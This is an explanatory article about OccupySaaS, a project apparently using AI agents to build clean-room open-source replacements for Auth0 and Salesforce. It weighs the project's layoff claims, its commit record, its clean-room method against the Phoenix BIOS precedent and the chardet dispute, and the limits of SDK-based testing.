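# OccupySaaS: the project using AI to rebuild Auth0 and Salesforce as free software

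## What is OccupySaaS?

OccupySaaS is an open-source project that publishes free replacements for online services that businesses normally rent. In October 2026 its anonymous developers, who say the technology industry laid them off, released two programs written largely by AI models. ZeroAuthy imitates Auth0, a service that logs people in to websites and apps. SalesCompel imitates Salesforce, which companies use to keep records of their customers and sales. The developers call the project a protest and named it after Occupy Wall Street, the movement against economic inequality that occupied a New York park in 2011. Both programs are unfinished, and the developers advise businesses not to rely on them yet.

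ZeroAuthy's code went public on 14 October 2026 and SalesCompel's on 15 October. The project's home page, *They laid us off. We're rebuilding their SaaS* (2026), gives both dates, as does *OccupySaaS* (2026), an article in the French trade publication Le Monde Informatique. On 3 November, Downes (2026) shared a link to the project in his newsletter about online learning, in *They laid us off. We're rebuilding their SaaS*. He liked the idea and expected people to build better things on such platforms once somebody had opened them up.

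Wide press coverage began the next day, 4 November, with Tom's Hardware's *Disgruntled software developers start ambitious open-source revolt*, which tied the project to customers' weariness with subscriptions and price rises. The project released ZeroAuthy's first release candidate, a test version before the finished release, on 4 November according to Le Monde Informatique, or 5 November according to Cornelißen (2026) in *OccupySaaS baut Auth0 und Salesforce nach*. On 6 November, Legouge (2026), in *« Ils nous ont licenciés, on reconstruit leurs logiciels »*, counted more than 150,000 lines of code after three weeks, with the AI model Claude as co-author of nearly two thirds of the changes. More stories ran in Italy and Germany on 22 and 23 November, including Tgcom24's *OccupySaaS, licenziati dal settore tech a causa dell'Ia rifanno i programmi* (2026) and BornCity's *OccupySaaS* (2026).

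### Two subscriptions in a small shop

The "SaaS" in OccupySaaS stands for "software as a service", which is software that runs on the vendor's computers and that customers rent by subscription. For example, a small bicycle shop might use Auth0 to let customers log in to its website and see their orders, while its five salespeople use Salesforce in their work with cycling clubs and hire firms. The shop has no copy of either program. It uses both over the internet and loses access if it stops paying.

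Most of the traffic between the shop and Auth0 is invisible to the shop's customers. In a common arrangement, a login goes like this:

1. A customer clicks "log in", and the shop's website sends her browser to a login page that Auth0 runs.
2. She types her password there. Auth0 checks it and sends her browser back to the shop with a short code.
3. The shop's server passes that code to Auth0 and gets back tokens, small pieces of signed data, one of which identifies the customer.
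4. The shop's server checks the signature against keys that Auth0 publishes, then sets a cookie in her browser so that she stays logged in.

At no point does the shop handle her password, which is a large part of what it pays for.

The messages in those steps belong to Auth0's API (application programming interface), the set of requests a service accepts from other programs and the answers it gives. Salesforce also has an API, so when a cycling club places a big order on the website, the shop's server can send Salesforce a request to create a record for the club, and nobody has to type it in. AI agents have recently started using APIs too. In April 2026 the programmer Simon Willison posted a passage on his weblog arguing that an API is now a selling point, because customers want AI agents to do work for them inside the services they pay for.

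Part of Auth0's API follows open standards. OAuth 2.0 is the standard for granting one program access to another, and OpenID Connect (OIDC) builds on it to tell a program who has logged in. Anyone may write a server that follows these standards, and free ones already exist. Zorz (2026), in *Ory Hydra*, describes a free, open-source server that issues and validates tokens under both. But Auth0 also has requests of its own, such as those for managing users and their roles, and a shop whose website relies on them can't simply switch to a server that supports only the standards.

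The shop's programmer usually uses an SDK (software development kit) instead of writing the requests by hand. An SDK is a code library that a vendor publishes for customers to build into their own programs so they can use its API. Auth0 has many of these, including one for apps on Apple devices. The programmer adds the library, fills in the address of the shop's Auth0 account, and calls a function such as "log in". The library then sends the right messages in the right order.

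OccupySaaS's central promise for ZeroAuthy is that a programmer can change that address to point an existing Auth0 SDK at a ZeroAuthy server, and the SDK will work with no code changes. A program that can replace another without changes to the software that depends on it is called a drop-in replacement. The bicycle shop would edit a setting, where it might otherwise have to rewrite its website's login code. It would still have to move its customers' accounts to the new server.

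### Why companies depend on Auth0 and Salesforce

Auth0 belongs to Okta, which sells identity software, used to control who can access what. A basic login is easy to build. The harder part is everything around it, such as password resets, codes sent by text message and logins through Google or Microsoft. A mistake in any of these can let a stranger into a customer's account, so many firms prefer to pay a specialist.

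Firms that sell software to other firms have another reason to subscribe to Auth0. Their large buyers want employees to sign in with their existing company account (single sign-on) and to lose access to every program at once when they leave. Auth0 advertises both as ready-made features for start-ups, along with help in passing buyers' security reviews and visibility to "17,000+ enterprise buyers" in Okta's network, a figure that doesn't count Auth0's own customers. A subscription therefore offers a young company a route to customers as well as code.

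Okta, whose products include Auth0, is a big target for a project a few weeks old. It took in $834 million across all its products in the quarter that ended on 31 October 2026, 12.4% more than a year earlier, according to EconoTimes' *Okta Shares Fall 9% After Mixed Fiscal 2027 Fourth-Quarter Outlook* (2026). The company is also moving into security for AI agents, and Alspach (2026), in *Okta Sees ‘Breakout Quarter’ With Partners Amid Agentic Identity Push*, reports that outside partners took part in all 20 of its largest deals that quarter.

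Salesforce sells customer relationship management (CRM) software, which records a company's customers, contacts and sales. In the bicycle shop, each club has an entry called an account, and the people who place the club's orders are its contacts. Before calling a club, a salesperson can see who last spoke to it and what it bought.

The shop's dependence on Salesforce grows over time. It might start with plain records, then have Salesforce alert the manager whenever a quote passes a certain sum. Later it might redesign the screens to suit how it takes orders, and buy another company's add-on that works only inside Salesforce. After a few years, parts of the shop's sales process are recorded only in Salesforce. Le Monde Informatique points out that even if a rival accepts all the same API requests, the customer still has to redo its customisations, automations and add-ons. Changing an address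 therefore completes much less of the move from Salesforce than from Auth0.

OccupySaaS describes logins and CRM as "the two subscriptions almost every company pays for and almost nobody loves". It gives no figures for either claim, and many small firms use a spreadsheet instead of a CRM. Starting with these two still makes sense, because a lot of other software depends on Auth0 and Salesforce, and both have public API documentation to work from.

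### What the project offers instead

OccupySaaS gives its code away under Apache-2.0, an open-source licence that lets anyone use, change and sell the code. The bicycle shop could run ZeroAuthy without paying or asking permission, and could hire a programmer to add a missing feature. A competitor of Okta could build a paid product on the same code. If the founders lost interest, anyone with a copy of the code could keep using it.

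The software is free in that the shop would pay no licence fee, but the shop would have to run it or find someone who could. Running software on servers one controls, instead of renting it as a service, is called self-hosting. ZeroAuthy is a single server program that stores its data in one of three common databases, so an ordinary web developer could install it. The shop would also have to do the rest of the vendor's job, which includes paying for the server, making backups, installing security fixes and fixing login failures at any hour.

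The project's founders say AI coding agents make it possible for them to take on such large products. These agents use a large language model (LLM) to work toward a goal set by a programmer, writing code, running it and fixing errors over many steps with little human input. The Pragmatic Engineer's *I replaced a $120/year micro-SaaS in 20 minutes with LLM-generated code* describes a small example, in which a working engineer used Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, to rebuild one minor paid service. Codex got the page layout wrong at first, and the engineer had to reject the result and choose the technical approach. The engineer writes that a non-developer could probably have managed, but more slowly.

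OccupySaaS applies the same kind of tool to far bigger products. People use public documentation to write a description of what the service does, agents write the code from that description, and a human reviews the changes before they go in. The project couldn't take the original programs apart anyway because, as Tom's Hardware notes, Auth0 and Salesforce run on their owners' servers.

### Three complaints

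The home page sets out the protest under three headings, on pricing, lock-in and layoffs.

OccupySaaS objects to per-seat pricing, which charges a customer for each person who uses the software. It calls this "a *tax* on growth" and says infrastructure "shouldn't charge rent by the head". If the bicycle shop goes from five salespeople to six, its Salesforce bill rises by a fifth. Vendors can fairly reply that a shop with five salespeople pays far less this way than a bank with five thousand. The complaint also fits Salesforce better than Auth0, because a login service mostly serves the shop's customers. Cornelißen accordingly speaks of vendors that bill per user or per login. The complaint still applies loosely to Auth0, since its bill also grows with the business.

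Lock-in is the cost and difficulty of leaving a vendor, which keep customers paying. In the project's words, "Proprietary APIs, export walls and surprise price hikes keep customers captive." These problems reinforce each other. If the shop's website works only with Auth0's API and its customer accounts are hard to export, the shop will accept a price rise that would otherwise have made it leave. The project offers drop-in compatibility, which is a good answer to proprietary APIs. It does little about export walls, because customers still have to get their data out of the old service. It could help with prices even for a customer who stays, provided the vendor believes that the customer could leave.

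The layoffs complaint reads, "A million engineers were let go while the platforms kept growing." BornCity found that the founders give no reliable source for the million, and nobody outside the project knows which companies they worked for. Free software can address the other two complaints by lowering a bill or loosening a contract, but it doesn't give anyone their job back. The layoffs complaint explains why these people are doing the work, and perhaps why they do it in public. Its heading, "They cut us. We *commit*", puns on the programming term for a recorded change to a project's code, which carries its author and date.

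Avico (2026) writes in *OccupySaaS, sviluppatori licenziati a causa dell'IA ricreano i programmi e li distribuiscono* that OccupySaaS mainly targets subscriptions, paid licences and dependence on a platform. That reading fits the products, which a customer can judge without having a view on who lost a job or why.

### Proposed next targets

OccupySaaS marks logins and CRM as "occupied" and lists five more categories of software as proposals:

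- **Docs and wikis:** shared pages where a team writes down what it knows, such as how the bicycle shop handles returns. The project objects to putting a company's own writing behind a seat licence.
- **Issue tracking:** lists of bugs and tasks, with who is working on each. The proposal includes a compatible API, so that tools already connected to a paid tracker would keep working.
- **Feature flags:** switches that turn part of a program on or off for chosen users. The shop could show a new checkout page to one customer in ten and withdraw it if sales fell.
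- **Observability:** the logs and measurements that engineers use to find out why a system is slow or broken. Here the project's quarrel is with charges per gigabyte of data.
- **Customer support:** a help desk with a shared inbox and a library of answers.

The project calls these categories "open for discussion, not commitments". It names no vendor for any of them and sets no dates. Anyone can use a form on GitHub, the site that hosts the code, to publicly suggest which service to occupy next and explain why.

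## Who is behind it, and what are they protesting?

The founders of OccupySaaS do not give their names or mention a former employer. Delacroix (2026), in *Occupy Saas*, found no way to contact them except through a website, the code on GitHub and three donation platforms, including Buy Me a Coffee. BornCity reports that they want the donations for infrastructure.

The founders have understandable reasons to stay anonymous. Delacroix mentions the risk of lawsuits, since Okta and Salesforce may object to copies of their products. An engineer looking for work may also not want the next employer to find the project. But anonymity means that nobody outside the project can check the story behind the protest. The founders may have lost jobs at Salesforce or at a bank, or they may not have lost jobs at all. Their rules let former employees of Auth0, Okta and Salesforce contribute as long as they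 bring no confidential knowledge, but outsiders can't tell whether any have done so.

### Did AI cost them their jobs?

Much of the coverage in late November described the project's developers as programmers whom AI had replaced. Avico states this as fact, while BornCity and Cornelißen attribute the claim to the developers. Delacroix writes that they are rebuilding the software that replaced them, which makes little sense, since Auth0 is a login service and Salesforce is a customer database.

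On their home page, the founders call themselves "laid-off engineers, armed with AI and public documentation". They present AI as a tool they use and never say they lost their jobs because of it. Yet Avico quotes that line, in Italian, under a headline that blames AI.

Le Monde Informatique pointed out on 10 November that the founders hadn't explained why they left their jobs, so nothing public shows that AI was the cause, or that they ever worked for the vendors they are copying. The claim that they lost their jobs to AI probably spread from ANSA, the Italian news agency, which ran a headline on 22 November about developers laid off because of AI. Cornelißen and Delacroix both link to that story, Avico credits the agency, and BornCity refers to Italian reports, so the four articles don't confirm the claim independently.

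ANSA may have known more. According to Delacroix, the agency reported that the members describe themselves as technology workers laid off between 2024 and 2026. If the founders told ANSA that, they may also have blamed AI. But their timeline of "the great tech layoffs" starts in 2022, and ChatGPT only came out at the end of that year, so AI can't explain the early cuts. Le Monde Informatique's version is safer until a founder publicly gives a reason.

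### What the commit record shows

ZeroAuthy's public commit history on GitHub is better evidence of who does the work. Cornelißen went through it and found that one account made about 1,200 of the nearly 1,300 commits. Another 66 had Claude, Anthropic's AI model, as their author, which leaves around 30 for everybody else. Cornelißen concludes that the collective is currently mostly one person with AI agents and a handful of helpers.

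Claude is the author of only one commit in twenty, which seems hard to reconcile with Legouge's report that it co-signed nearly two thirds of the changes.

The two counts probably differ because of how programmers give credit. Suppose a developer asks Claude to add password resets. Claude writes the code, and the developer reviews it and saves it as a commit from her own account. Git, which keeps the record, lists her as the author. A line in the commit's description, which some coding agents add automatically, names Claude as co-author. Cornelißen would count this commit as the developer's, while Legouge would include it among those that Claude co-signed. Claude is listed as the author only when a commit is made under its own name, which can happen when an agent works directly on GitHub.

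Both figures can be right, because two thirds of 1,300 commits is about 870, and nearly all of those could be among the 1,200 from the main account.

The two counts may also cover different things. Legouge published on 6 November and wrote about the whole project, while Cornelißen published on 23 November and counted only ZeroAuthy. Claude's share could easily have changed in those seventeen days. Anyone can download the code and count both kinds of credit on the same day, but that wouldn't measure how much Claude wrote. The co-author line looks the same whether Claude produced a whole feature or corrected one word, and a developer can leave it out.

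Several anonymous people could share one account to protect themselves, and someone who writes specifications or tests the software may never make a commit. Still, if a crowd of laid-off engineers is building ZeroAuthy, there is very little trace of it. This matters because the project's method depends on keeping the people who write the specification separate from those who build the software.

The speed also points to heavy use of AI. Legouge's figure of more than 150,000 lines in three weeks comes to about 7,000 lines a day. Nobody types that much, and one person could hardly read it all carefully. Test code and generated files may inflate the total, and some of the work may date from before the code went public.

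### A million engineers

The founders' slogan, "We are the 1,000,000", is based on their unsourced figure of a million laid-off engineers. Delacroix describes them as a million engineers replaced by algorithms, but the founders didn't write that algorithms replaced them.

Layoffs.fyi, a website that adds up announced job cuts at technology companies, counted roughly 700,000 worldwide from 2022 to 2025, the years on the founders' timeline. The real total is higher because trackers like this miss small firms and unannounced cuts. A million is therefore believable for everyone who lost a job in the industry, but it looks much too high for engineers alone, since layoff counts also include recruiters, salespeople and support staff. The founders may have applied a figure for the whole industry to their own profession.

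Employers attribute far fewer layoffs to AI. The investment bank Goldman Sachs counts 208,000 such layoffs in the United States from May 2023 through October 2026, across all kinds of work. *Employment Data Now Showing Signs of AI Taking Human Jobs* (Wilkins, 2026) lists technology, marketing, graphic design and customer service as the fields that AI has hit hardest. Even if all 208,000 people had been engineers, they would be about a fifth of the founders' figure of one million.

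Only about 1,200 of these layoffs came in October 2026, the month OccupySaaS launched, compared with an average of nearly 5,000 a month over the whole period.

The Goldman figure also has weaknesses. Faisal (2026), in *Goldman Sachs Counts 208,000 AI-Linked Layoffs Since 2023*, points out that the bank hasn't shown how it counts. International Business Times UK's *Goldman Sachs Tracks 208,000 Announced AI Layoffs* (2026) describes the layoffs as announced cuts, and companies don't always cut as many jobs as they announce. Goldman compares the layoffs with 319,000 new construction jobs building data centres, and Lichtenberg (2026) takes the headline of *Goldman crunches the layoff math* from that comparison. The new jobs may offset the losses in the national total, but few programmers can move straight into construction.

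### AI washing

Firms sometimes blame AI for job cuts they would have made anyway. Critics call this "AI washing", and BornCity and Delacroix both report that Sam Altman, the head of OpenAI, has used the term. A company that hired too many people, or whose sales have slowed, looks better to investors if it can say that AI now does the work. BornCity notes that Amazon, Meta and Microsoft plan to cut administrative jobs while investing heavily in AI. In such cases, people may have lost their jobs because the company needed money for data centres, even though AI does none of their work.

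Wilkins is also sceptical because he finds little evidence that AI has made workplaces more productive. He cites the analytics company ActivTrak, which found that people who use AI work 90 minutes a day longer than those who don't. But longer hours don't mean that less gets done, and OccupySaaS is itself evidence that AI can make programming more productive. One account, with Claude's help, produced a working imitation of much of Auth0 within weeks. A software company that sees this has reason to think it needs fewer engineers, even if running a service for paying customers takes far more than a first version of the code.

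The best reply to the charge of AI washing uses data that don't depend on what employers say. Faisal reports that unemployment among young technology workers has risen above the rate for technology workers overall. He also cites a Stanford study from August 2026, which found that employment among people aged 22 to 25 in the occupations most exposed to AI was about 19% below its expected level. But a firm can reduce its junior staff by not replacing those who leave, so these data are evidence about hiring at least as much as about layoffs.

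The two explanations also overlap. *AI could displace one in 11 workers, Goldman says* (Lichtenberg, 2026) reports that Joseph Briggs, an economist at Goldman, found that companies have historically saved their automation layoffs for downturns. For example, a firm whose software made ten clerks unnecessary two years ago might let them go only when sales fall. If it blames the economy, those layoffs won't be counted as AI layoffs. Such omissions would make Goldman's figure too low, while AI washing would make it too high, and nobody knows which effect is larger.

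The official reason for a layoff may matter less to the worker than its consequences. Goldman sees lasting harm from AI layoffs, Lichtenberg reports in *Goldman says AI layoffs are starting to leave a 'long-lasting' scar* (2026). Workers aged 35 and over are suffering most, and finding a new job takes about five weeks longer.

### Cuts at Salesforce and Okta

Salesforce and Okta, whose products OccupySaaS copies, have both cut staff. Salesforce laid off about 5,000 people in 2025, around 4,000 of them in September, according to *The quiet collapse of the SaaS golden age*, an anonymous web page that draws on press reports. Salesforce reportedly cut nearly 1,000 more jobs in February 2026. Okta laid off about 400 people in February 2024, saying its costs were too high, and about 180 more a year later.

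Salesforce's chief executive, Marc Benioff, also said in early 2025 that the company might hire no new software engineers that year, because AI had made the existing ones more productive. Critics of AI washing distrust this kind of statement, especially from a company that sells AI agents and can use it as advertising. If he meant it, though, engineers laid off elsewhere had one fewer large employer to apply to, which layoff counts would not show.

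None of this connects the founders to either company, and they needn't have worked at one to resent it.

### What they take from Occupy Wall Street

The founders borrow the project's name and much of its language from the Occupy protesters of 2011, who spoke for "the 99%" against the richest 1%. They write on the OccupySaaS home page that software built by the 99% belongs to the 99%, and a banner there reads "Fork the 1%" (to fork a project is to copy its code and develop it separately). They call the two programs "two towers" and their list of future targets an "occupation map". The logo shows a raised fist holding a laptop over a crowd with placards.

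The founders also admire Occupy for having no leaders and making decisions in open assemblies, and they promise to choose their own targets in public. They say they want the same spirit with "no marches, no property damage".

One account has made more than nine in ten of the commits to ZeroAuthy, which fits badly with the idea of a leaderless movement. Anyone may propose a target, but whoever controls that account can decide what gets built. Occupy's protesters also argued face to face in a park, while nobody can tell how many people are in OccupySaaS's assembly.

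An occupation puts pressure on people by getting in their way. The campers in Zuccotti Park filled a space that others wanted back, and the authorities cleared it after two months. ZeroAuthy leaves Okta's servers running as before, so it puts pressure on Okta only if customers leave or use the free version to bargain. But the police can't clear away code that people have already copied, so the protest could continue even if its founders lose interest.

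The talk of the 99% is also awkward, because software engineers earn more than most people and the direct savings would go to businesses. If a bank replaced Salesforce with SalesCompel, the bank would keep the money, which is not what the Occupy Wall Street protesters wanted. The founders have a stronger argument when they speak as workers who object to paying rent on tools that people like them built.

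### How people received it

Downes, who found the project through a post by the technology writer Jon Udell, was one of the first to welcome it publicly. He focused on what people might build next and said little about the layoffs.

Tom's Hardware treated OccupySaaS as a revolt by users tired of subscriptions, and mentioned it alongside ArtCraft, an alternative to Adobe's software that had recently caused excitement. But the protesters in the founders' slogan are laid-off engineers.

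Avico offers another comparison, to the American protests against data centres and the students who boo speakers on AI at universities. OccupySaaS may share their anger about jobs, but it does not object to AI itself. It relies on Claude for much of its work, and Claude is also a service that Anthropic rents out by subscription. The founders object to who owns the software and what those owners charge for it, but so far they have not made the same complaint about AI companies.

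Other writers were impressed by the speed but doubtful about the result. Legouge asked whether anyone could compete with the software giants so easily, and answered "not so fast". Cornelißen sees the project as a way to put pressure on vendors, but not yet as a replacement for them.

Delacroix also reports a suspicion that the whole protest is marketing, but attributes it only to "certain observers". It isn't obvious what the founders would be marketing, since they sell nothing and can't use the project to impress an employer while they stay anonymous. But they could later start a company that charges to run ZeroAuthy for customers, which the licence allows. The story about laid-off engineers would then have given them a lot of free publicity.

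## How can a service be rebuilt without seeing its code?

OccupySaaS says it builds its programs in a clean room. In this method, the people who write the new code never see the original code and work only from a specification, a written description of what the program must do. Two programs that do the same job will resemble each other in places, but people who never saw the original code can't have copied it.

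### The BIOS that Phoenix copied

The best-known clean room dates from 1984. Every IBM PC contained a small program called the BIOS, which started the machine and let other software use the keyboard, screen and disks. A rival computer could run the same software only if its own BIOS answered the same calls in the same way. IBM had printed the BIOS's code in a technical manual, so rivals could easily copy it. Some did, and IBM sued them.

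Phoenix Technologies, a small software company in Massachusetts, split the work in two. One group read IBM's code and wrote a specification of what it did, including which calls it accepted and where it kept tables that other programs looked up. They gave this specification, but none of the code, to the engineers writing the new BIOS. History of Information's *Phoenix Technologies Produces the First Commercially Available IBM PC Compatible ROM Bios* calls the first group "contaminated" and the second "clean". By some accounts, there was only one clean engineer. Phoenix wanted someone who had never programmed the Intel chip in the IBM PC, and chose a specialist in a Texas Instruments processor.

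Phoenix also recorded everything that passed between the two sides. The finished code couldn't show who had read what, so Phoenix needed the records to prove that the two sides had stayed separate. Its customers needed that proof too, because they would be selling computers with Phoenix's BIOS inside. Phoenix charged them $290,000 for a licence and bought $2 million of insurance against copyright lawsuits.

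All this was expensive, even for a program of about eight kilobytes. The law firm Reed Smith's *Clean room coding in the age of AI* explains that a rigorous clean room takes two teams, often months or years of engineering, lawyers and extensive documentation. Accepting the owner's licence terms was usually cheaper. AI coding agents have changed that. Willison (2026), in *Can coding agents relicense open source through a “clean room” implementation*, writes that they can do a "weird version" of a clean room in hours.

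### OccupySaaS's five steps

OccupySaaS's home page sets out the method in five steps:

1. **Read public documents.** People turn the vendor's API documentation, open standards and the behaviour of its SDKs into a specification.
2. **Separate the two sides.** The people who write the specification don't build the software. Each program has a policy file called `CLEAN_ROOM.md`, and the project promises to record where every reference and every piece of test data came from.
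3. **Build with AI.** Agents work from the specification alone. They first write a contract, `openapi.yaml`, which lists the requests the server will accept and the form of each answer. Then they write the code, and then tests for it. A person reviews each change before it joins the main code.
4. **Test with the vendor's SDKs.** A "compatibility laboratory" runs the vendor's own public SDKs against the new server. If a customer's existing code doesn't work unchanged, the job isn't finished.
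5. **Release the result.** Anyone can download the program and run it on their own servers.

The project also lists what may and may not enter the clean room:

| Allowed | Forbidden |
|---|---|
| Public API documentation | Leaked or proprietary source code |
| Open standards | Decompiled programs |
| Behaviour of public SDKs | Confidential information from former employers |
| Results of black-box tests | Copied interface artwork and trademarks |

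A black-box test sends requests to a running service and records the responses without examining its code. Decompiling, by contrast, turns a compiled program back into something like its source code.

### One request, from a sentence to a test

To see how the steps fit together, suppose the bicycle shop's login vendor offers a request that "returns the date and time of a customer's last login". The shop uses it to find customers who have stopped visiting its website.

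**Step 1.** A specification writer reads that sentence and the technical details around it. She writes down the request's address, the name of the field in the answer, and the error for a customer who doesn't exist. The documentation doesn't cover customers who have opened an account but never logged in, so she creates such a customer in her own trial account with the vendor, sends the request, and gets back `null`, a standard marker for an empty value. She adds this to the specification and records the test as her source.

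**Step 2.** The builder receives the specification but not the vendor's documentation or her notes. If the builder asks a question, she answers it in writing and corrects the specification.

**Step 3.** An agent writes the contract. The entry for this request, slightly shortened, might look like this:

```yaml
/customers/{id}/last-login:
  get:
    responses:
      "200":
        content:
          application/json:
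            schema:
              type: object
              properties:
                last_login:
                  type: [string, "null"]
                  format: date-time
      "404":
        description: No such customer
```

The codes 200 and 404 mean "success" and "not found". The agent then writes code that looks up the customer and returns the stored time. It adds tests for a customer who logged in yesterday, one who has never logged in, and one who doesn't exist. All three tests pass, but the human reviewer sends the code back because the server answers requests without checking for a valid token.

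In step 4, the laboratory points the vendor's SDK at the new server and requests a customer's last login. The SDK reports an error because it accepts only universal time, 14:05, and the agent had written the time as 15:05 with a note that the local clock was an hour ahead. Both forms satisfy the contract, and the agent's own tests missed the problem because, like its code, they didn't account for the SDK's requirement. The specification writer adds the missing rule, the agent corrects the server, and the SDK test passes.

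**Step 5.** The project publishes the new version. The shop changes one address in its settings, and its list of absent customers appears as before.

Agents can also do much of the first step. MuleSoft, which Salesforce owns, publishes *generate-connectivity-knowledge*, a set of instructions for AI agents. An agent following them researches a service's API, writes an OpenAPI file (the same kind of contract), and tests every operation against the live service, fixing mistakes as it goes. MuleSoft wants to help customers connect to the service, but the file would be just as useful to someone copying the service.

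### How much a passing test proves

The SDK test is good because the vendor wrote the SDK to work with its own server. An agent that misreads the specification can make the same mistake in its code and its tests, but it can't change the vendor's SDK to match. Customers' programs already contain these SDKs, so the test is close to real use.

Still, an SDK can work perfectly with a server that does nothing useful, and programmers often test against such servers. MuleSoft has a tool that reads an API description and returns the example responses written in it. Stainless, a company that generates SDKs, tests them against a mock server built from an OpenAPI file, according to its *Frequently Asked Questions (FAQs)*. It leaves these tests off in new projects because the mock server handles some unusual cases badly.

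In the bicycle shop example, a server that gave every customer the same login time could pass a weak test. A better test would log a customer in and then check that the time had changed.

This problem is more serious in login software. An SDK test can show that the right password works, but a server that accepted every password would also pass. Testers also have to try wrong passwords, expired tokens and login codes that another person has already used. This is an inference from how SDKs work, not evidence that ZeroAuthy has such a fault.

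The laboratory for SalesCompel works offline and compares the program with Salesforce's published API description. If that description is wrong, SalesCompel could presumably copy the mistake and still pass.

Using several kinds of test catches more errors than using one. *An x86-64 backend for raven-uxn* (Keeter, 2026) describes how Claude wrote low-level code for an emulator, a program that imitates another computer. The first version didn't compile, meaning it couldn't be turned into a runnable program. Once it compiled, it failed the unit tests, which check small parts separately. Once it passed those, it failed fuzz testing, which feeds a program large amounts of random input. Keeter needed all three layers to get working code. He also suspects that Claude did well because it could translate an existing version written for another processor, which is easier than starting from a high-level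 specification, as OccupySaaS's agents must.

Human review is supposed to catch what the tests miss, but it is hard to review roughly 7,000 lines of code a day. Some teams have deliberately stopped trying. Willison's *How StrongDM's AI team build serious software* describes a team whose rules include "Code must not be reviewed by humans". Its agents write code from specifications and keep working until the code passes a set of test scenarios. OccupySaaS promises human review, but if its reviewers only skim the code, it depends on its tests almost as much as StrongDM does.

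### What outsiders can and can't see

Cornelißen points out that a clean-room rebuild is easier for an online service than for desktop software, because the builders only have to imitate an API. The vendor also has to document that API so its customers' programmers can use it, and anyone with an account can check the documentation by sending requests.

But testing from outside covers only a small part of what a service can do. A login service with 20 on/off settings, for example, has just over a million possible combinations, so a thousand tests, each using a different combination, would cover about one in a thousand. Most combinations probably behave as expected, but someone copying the service can't know in advance which ones don't.

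Some of the missing behaviour isn't documented. A service might always return customers in alphabetical order, even though its documentation doesn't specify an order. The shop's programmer sees that the list is already sorted, so he or she doesn't write code to sort it. When the shop moves to a copy that returns the newest customers first, its staff page looks broken, even though the copy follows the documentation exactly.

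Vendors also keep some rules secret so that attackers can't work around them. For example, a login service may block an attempt because it comes from an unusual place or resembles an attack on another customer. A tester can see that the service blocked the login, but often can't tell why. Whoever is rebuilding the service then has to invent a rule without the vendor's record of attacks on thousands of customers.

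How a service handles scale is just as hard to see from outside. A response looks the same whether it comes from one server or a thousand, and API documentation rarely explains how the vendor keeps the service running when a data centre fails. A copy could pass every compatibility test with ten users and still fail when ten thousand log in at once. The specification could set a target for simultaneous logins, but the builders would have to work out for themselves how to meet it.

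### Who is on each side of the firewall?

OccupySaaS calls the separation between specification writers and builders a firewall. BornCity reports that separate teams do the analysis and the development, and that the group cites Phoenix's BIOS as a model. But a single account made most of ZeroAuthy's commits, so one person may have both written the specification and directed the agents that built from it.

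That would break the project's own rule, but it may matter less than it would have at Phoenix. Phoenix's specification writers had read IBM's code, and the firewall kept them from passing it on. OccupySaaS forbids both sides from using the vendor's private code. This suggests that someone who has read only public documents has no private code to pass on, even if they do both jobs.

The firewall would still help keep the documentation's wording and the SDKs' code out of the new program. It matters most if a contributor used to work for the vendor. The Sedona Conference's *Commentary on Use of Clean Rooms*, guidance from an American legal research group, covers how to screen employees who may have seen protected information, as well as the use of a "dirty team" for exposed people who still have some role in the project. Nobody outside OccupySaaS can screen its developers while they stay anonymous.

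Two separate agent sessions might be able to replace the two groups of people. A new session normally starts without any memory of earlier ones, so an agent that read the vendor's documentation in one session can't recall it in the next, whereas a human engineer can't forget on demand. The software can also log every file a session opens, which would be a more complete record than Phoenix's.

But how isolated a session is depends on which files and websites it can reach, and keeping the old code off the machine is a much stronger safeguard than telling the AI not to look at it. In the recent dispute over chardet, a free Python library that works out how a text file encodes its characters, the maintainer had used Claude to rewrite the library so that he could change its licence. According to Reed Smith, he wrote a design document, began with an empty repository and told the AI not to look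 at the old source code. Yet the Linux news site LWN reports that Willison observed the model did access that code at one point.

The person directing the AI can also carry knowledge between sessions. Meeker recounts in *The Chardet Controversy* that Mark Pilgrim, who originally wrote chardet, objected that the maintainers had "ample exposure" to his code. *License Laundering with a Large Language Model* (2026) similarly argues that the AI doesn't need a second team, but the human directing it still has all the old knowledge. The programmer Salvatore Sanfilippo (antirez) notes that a few hints can completely change the quality of an agent's work, even when the human never touches the code. Hints from someone who knows the original can therefore bypass the specification.

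Separate sessions could therefore serve much of the firewall's purpose, but only under stricter conditions than a written policy. The builder's session would need to run on a machine with no internet access and only the specification and ordinary programming tools. The project would also have to publish the human's instructions and the session's log. These conditions are inferred from what went wrong with chardet. OccupySaaS promises to record its references, which would cover what went into the specification but not what the building agents read.

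Automatic checks can help too. OpenCodeHub, another clean-room project, scans every file for names taken from projects it has promised not to copy, according to its *IP hygiene* document. OccupySaaS could scan for distinctive phrases from Auth0's documentation and SDKs, but not for Auth0's server code, because it has no copy to compare with.

### What the model saw in training

A firewall can keep a file out of a session, but it can't remove what the model learned in training. Phoenix could look for a programmer who had never used an Intel chip, but OccupySaaS can't easily find an AI model that writes good login software without having been trained on any. How much this matters depends on what was in the model's training data.

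The AI model behind the agents has probably seen Auth0's public documentation in training. The documentation is an allowed source, but the agents are supposed to work from the specification alone. If the specification has a gap, an agent may fill it from memory, and the project's records won't show where the answer came from. The answer may also be out of date, since Auth0 can change its API after the model's training ends.

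The model was probably also trained on Auth0's SDKs, which are published as open source. Their code shows which requests the server has to answer, but not how Auth0 stores passwords or decides that a login is suspicious. An agent could still reproduce passages from an SDK, for example where the SDK and the server both handle tokens, and the project would need to check for that.

The server code is different because Auth0 and Salesforce have never published it. Unless someone leaked it, the model had no obvious way to learn it, and a model can't recall code it never saw. This is an inference, but it is the best reason to think OccupySaaS's agents haven't copied the programs they imitate. The maintainer of chardet couldn't make the same argument, because the old code was public.

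The agents are more likely to reproduce code from another login server than from Auth0. The code of free login servers such as Ory Hydra is public, and a model has probably learned from several of them. If ZeroAuthy contains a long passage from one, the passage's author might have a complaint even if Auth0 does not.

Sanfilippo's own experiment shows how hard it is to tell whether a model has worked out code or recalled it from training. Starting with a plain-English description of what he wanted, he used Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, to write an emulator of the Z80, a 1970s processor, under what he considered fairer clean-room conditions. The emulator passed demanding Z80 tests, including tests of behaviour that the chip's makers never documented. Sanfilippo concluded that the model had assembled its knowledge much as a human programmer would. But its training data probably included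 dozens of Z80 emulators, and a copied emulator would pass the same tests.

Someone has to compare the code itself to find copying. Anyone can check a Z80 emulator by searching public emulators for matching passages. But only Okta can make the most important comparison for ZeroAuthy, because it has Auth0's server code and can download ZeroAuthy's.

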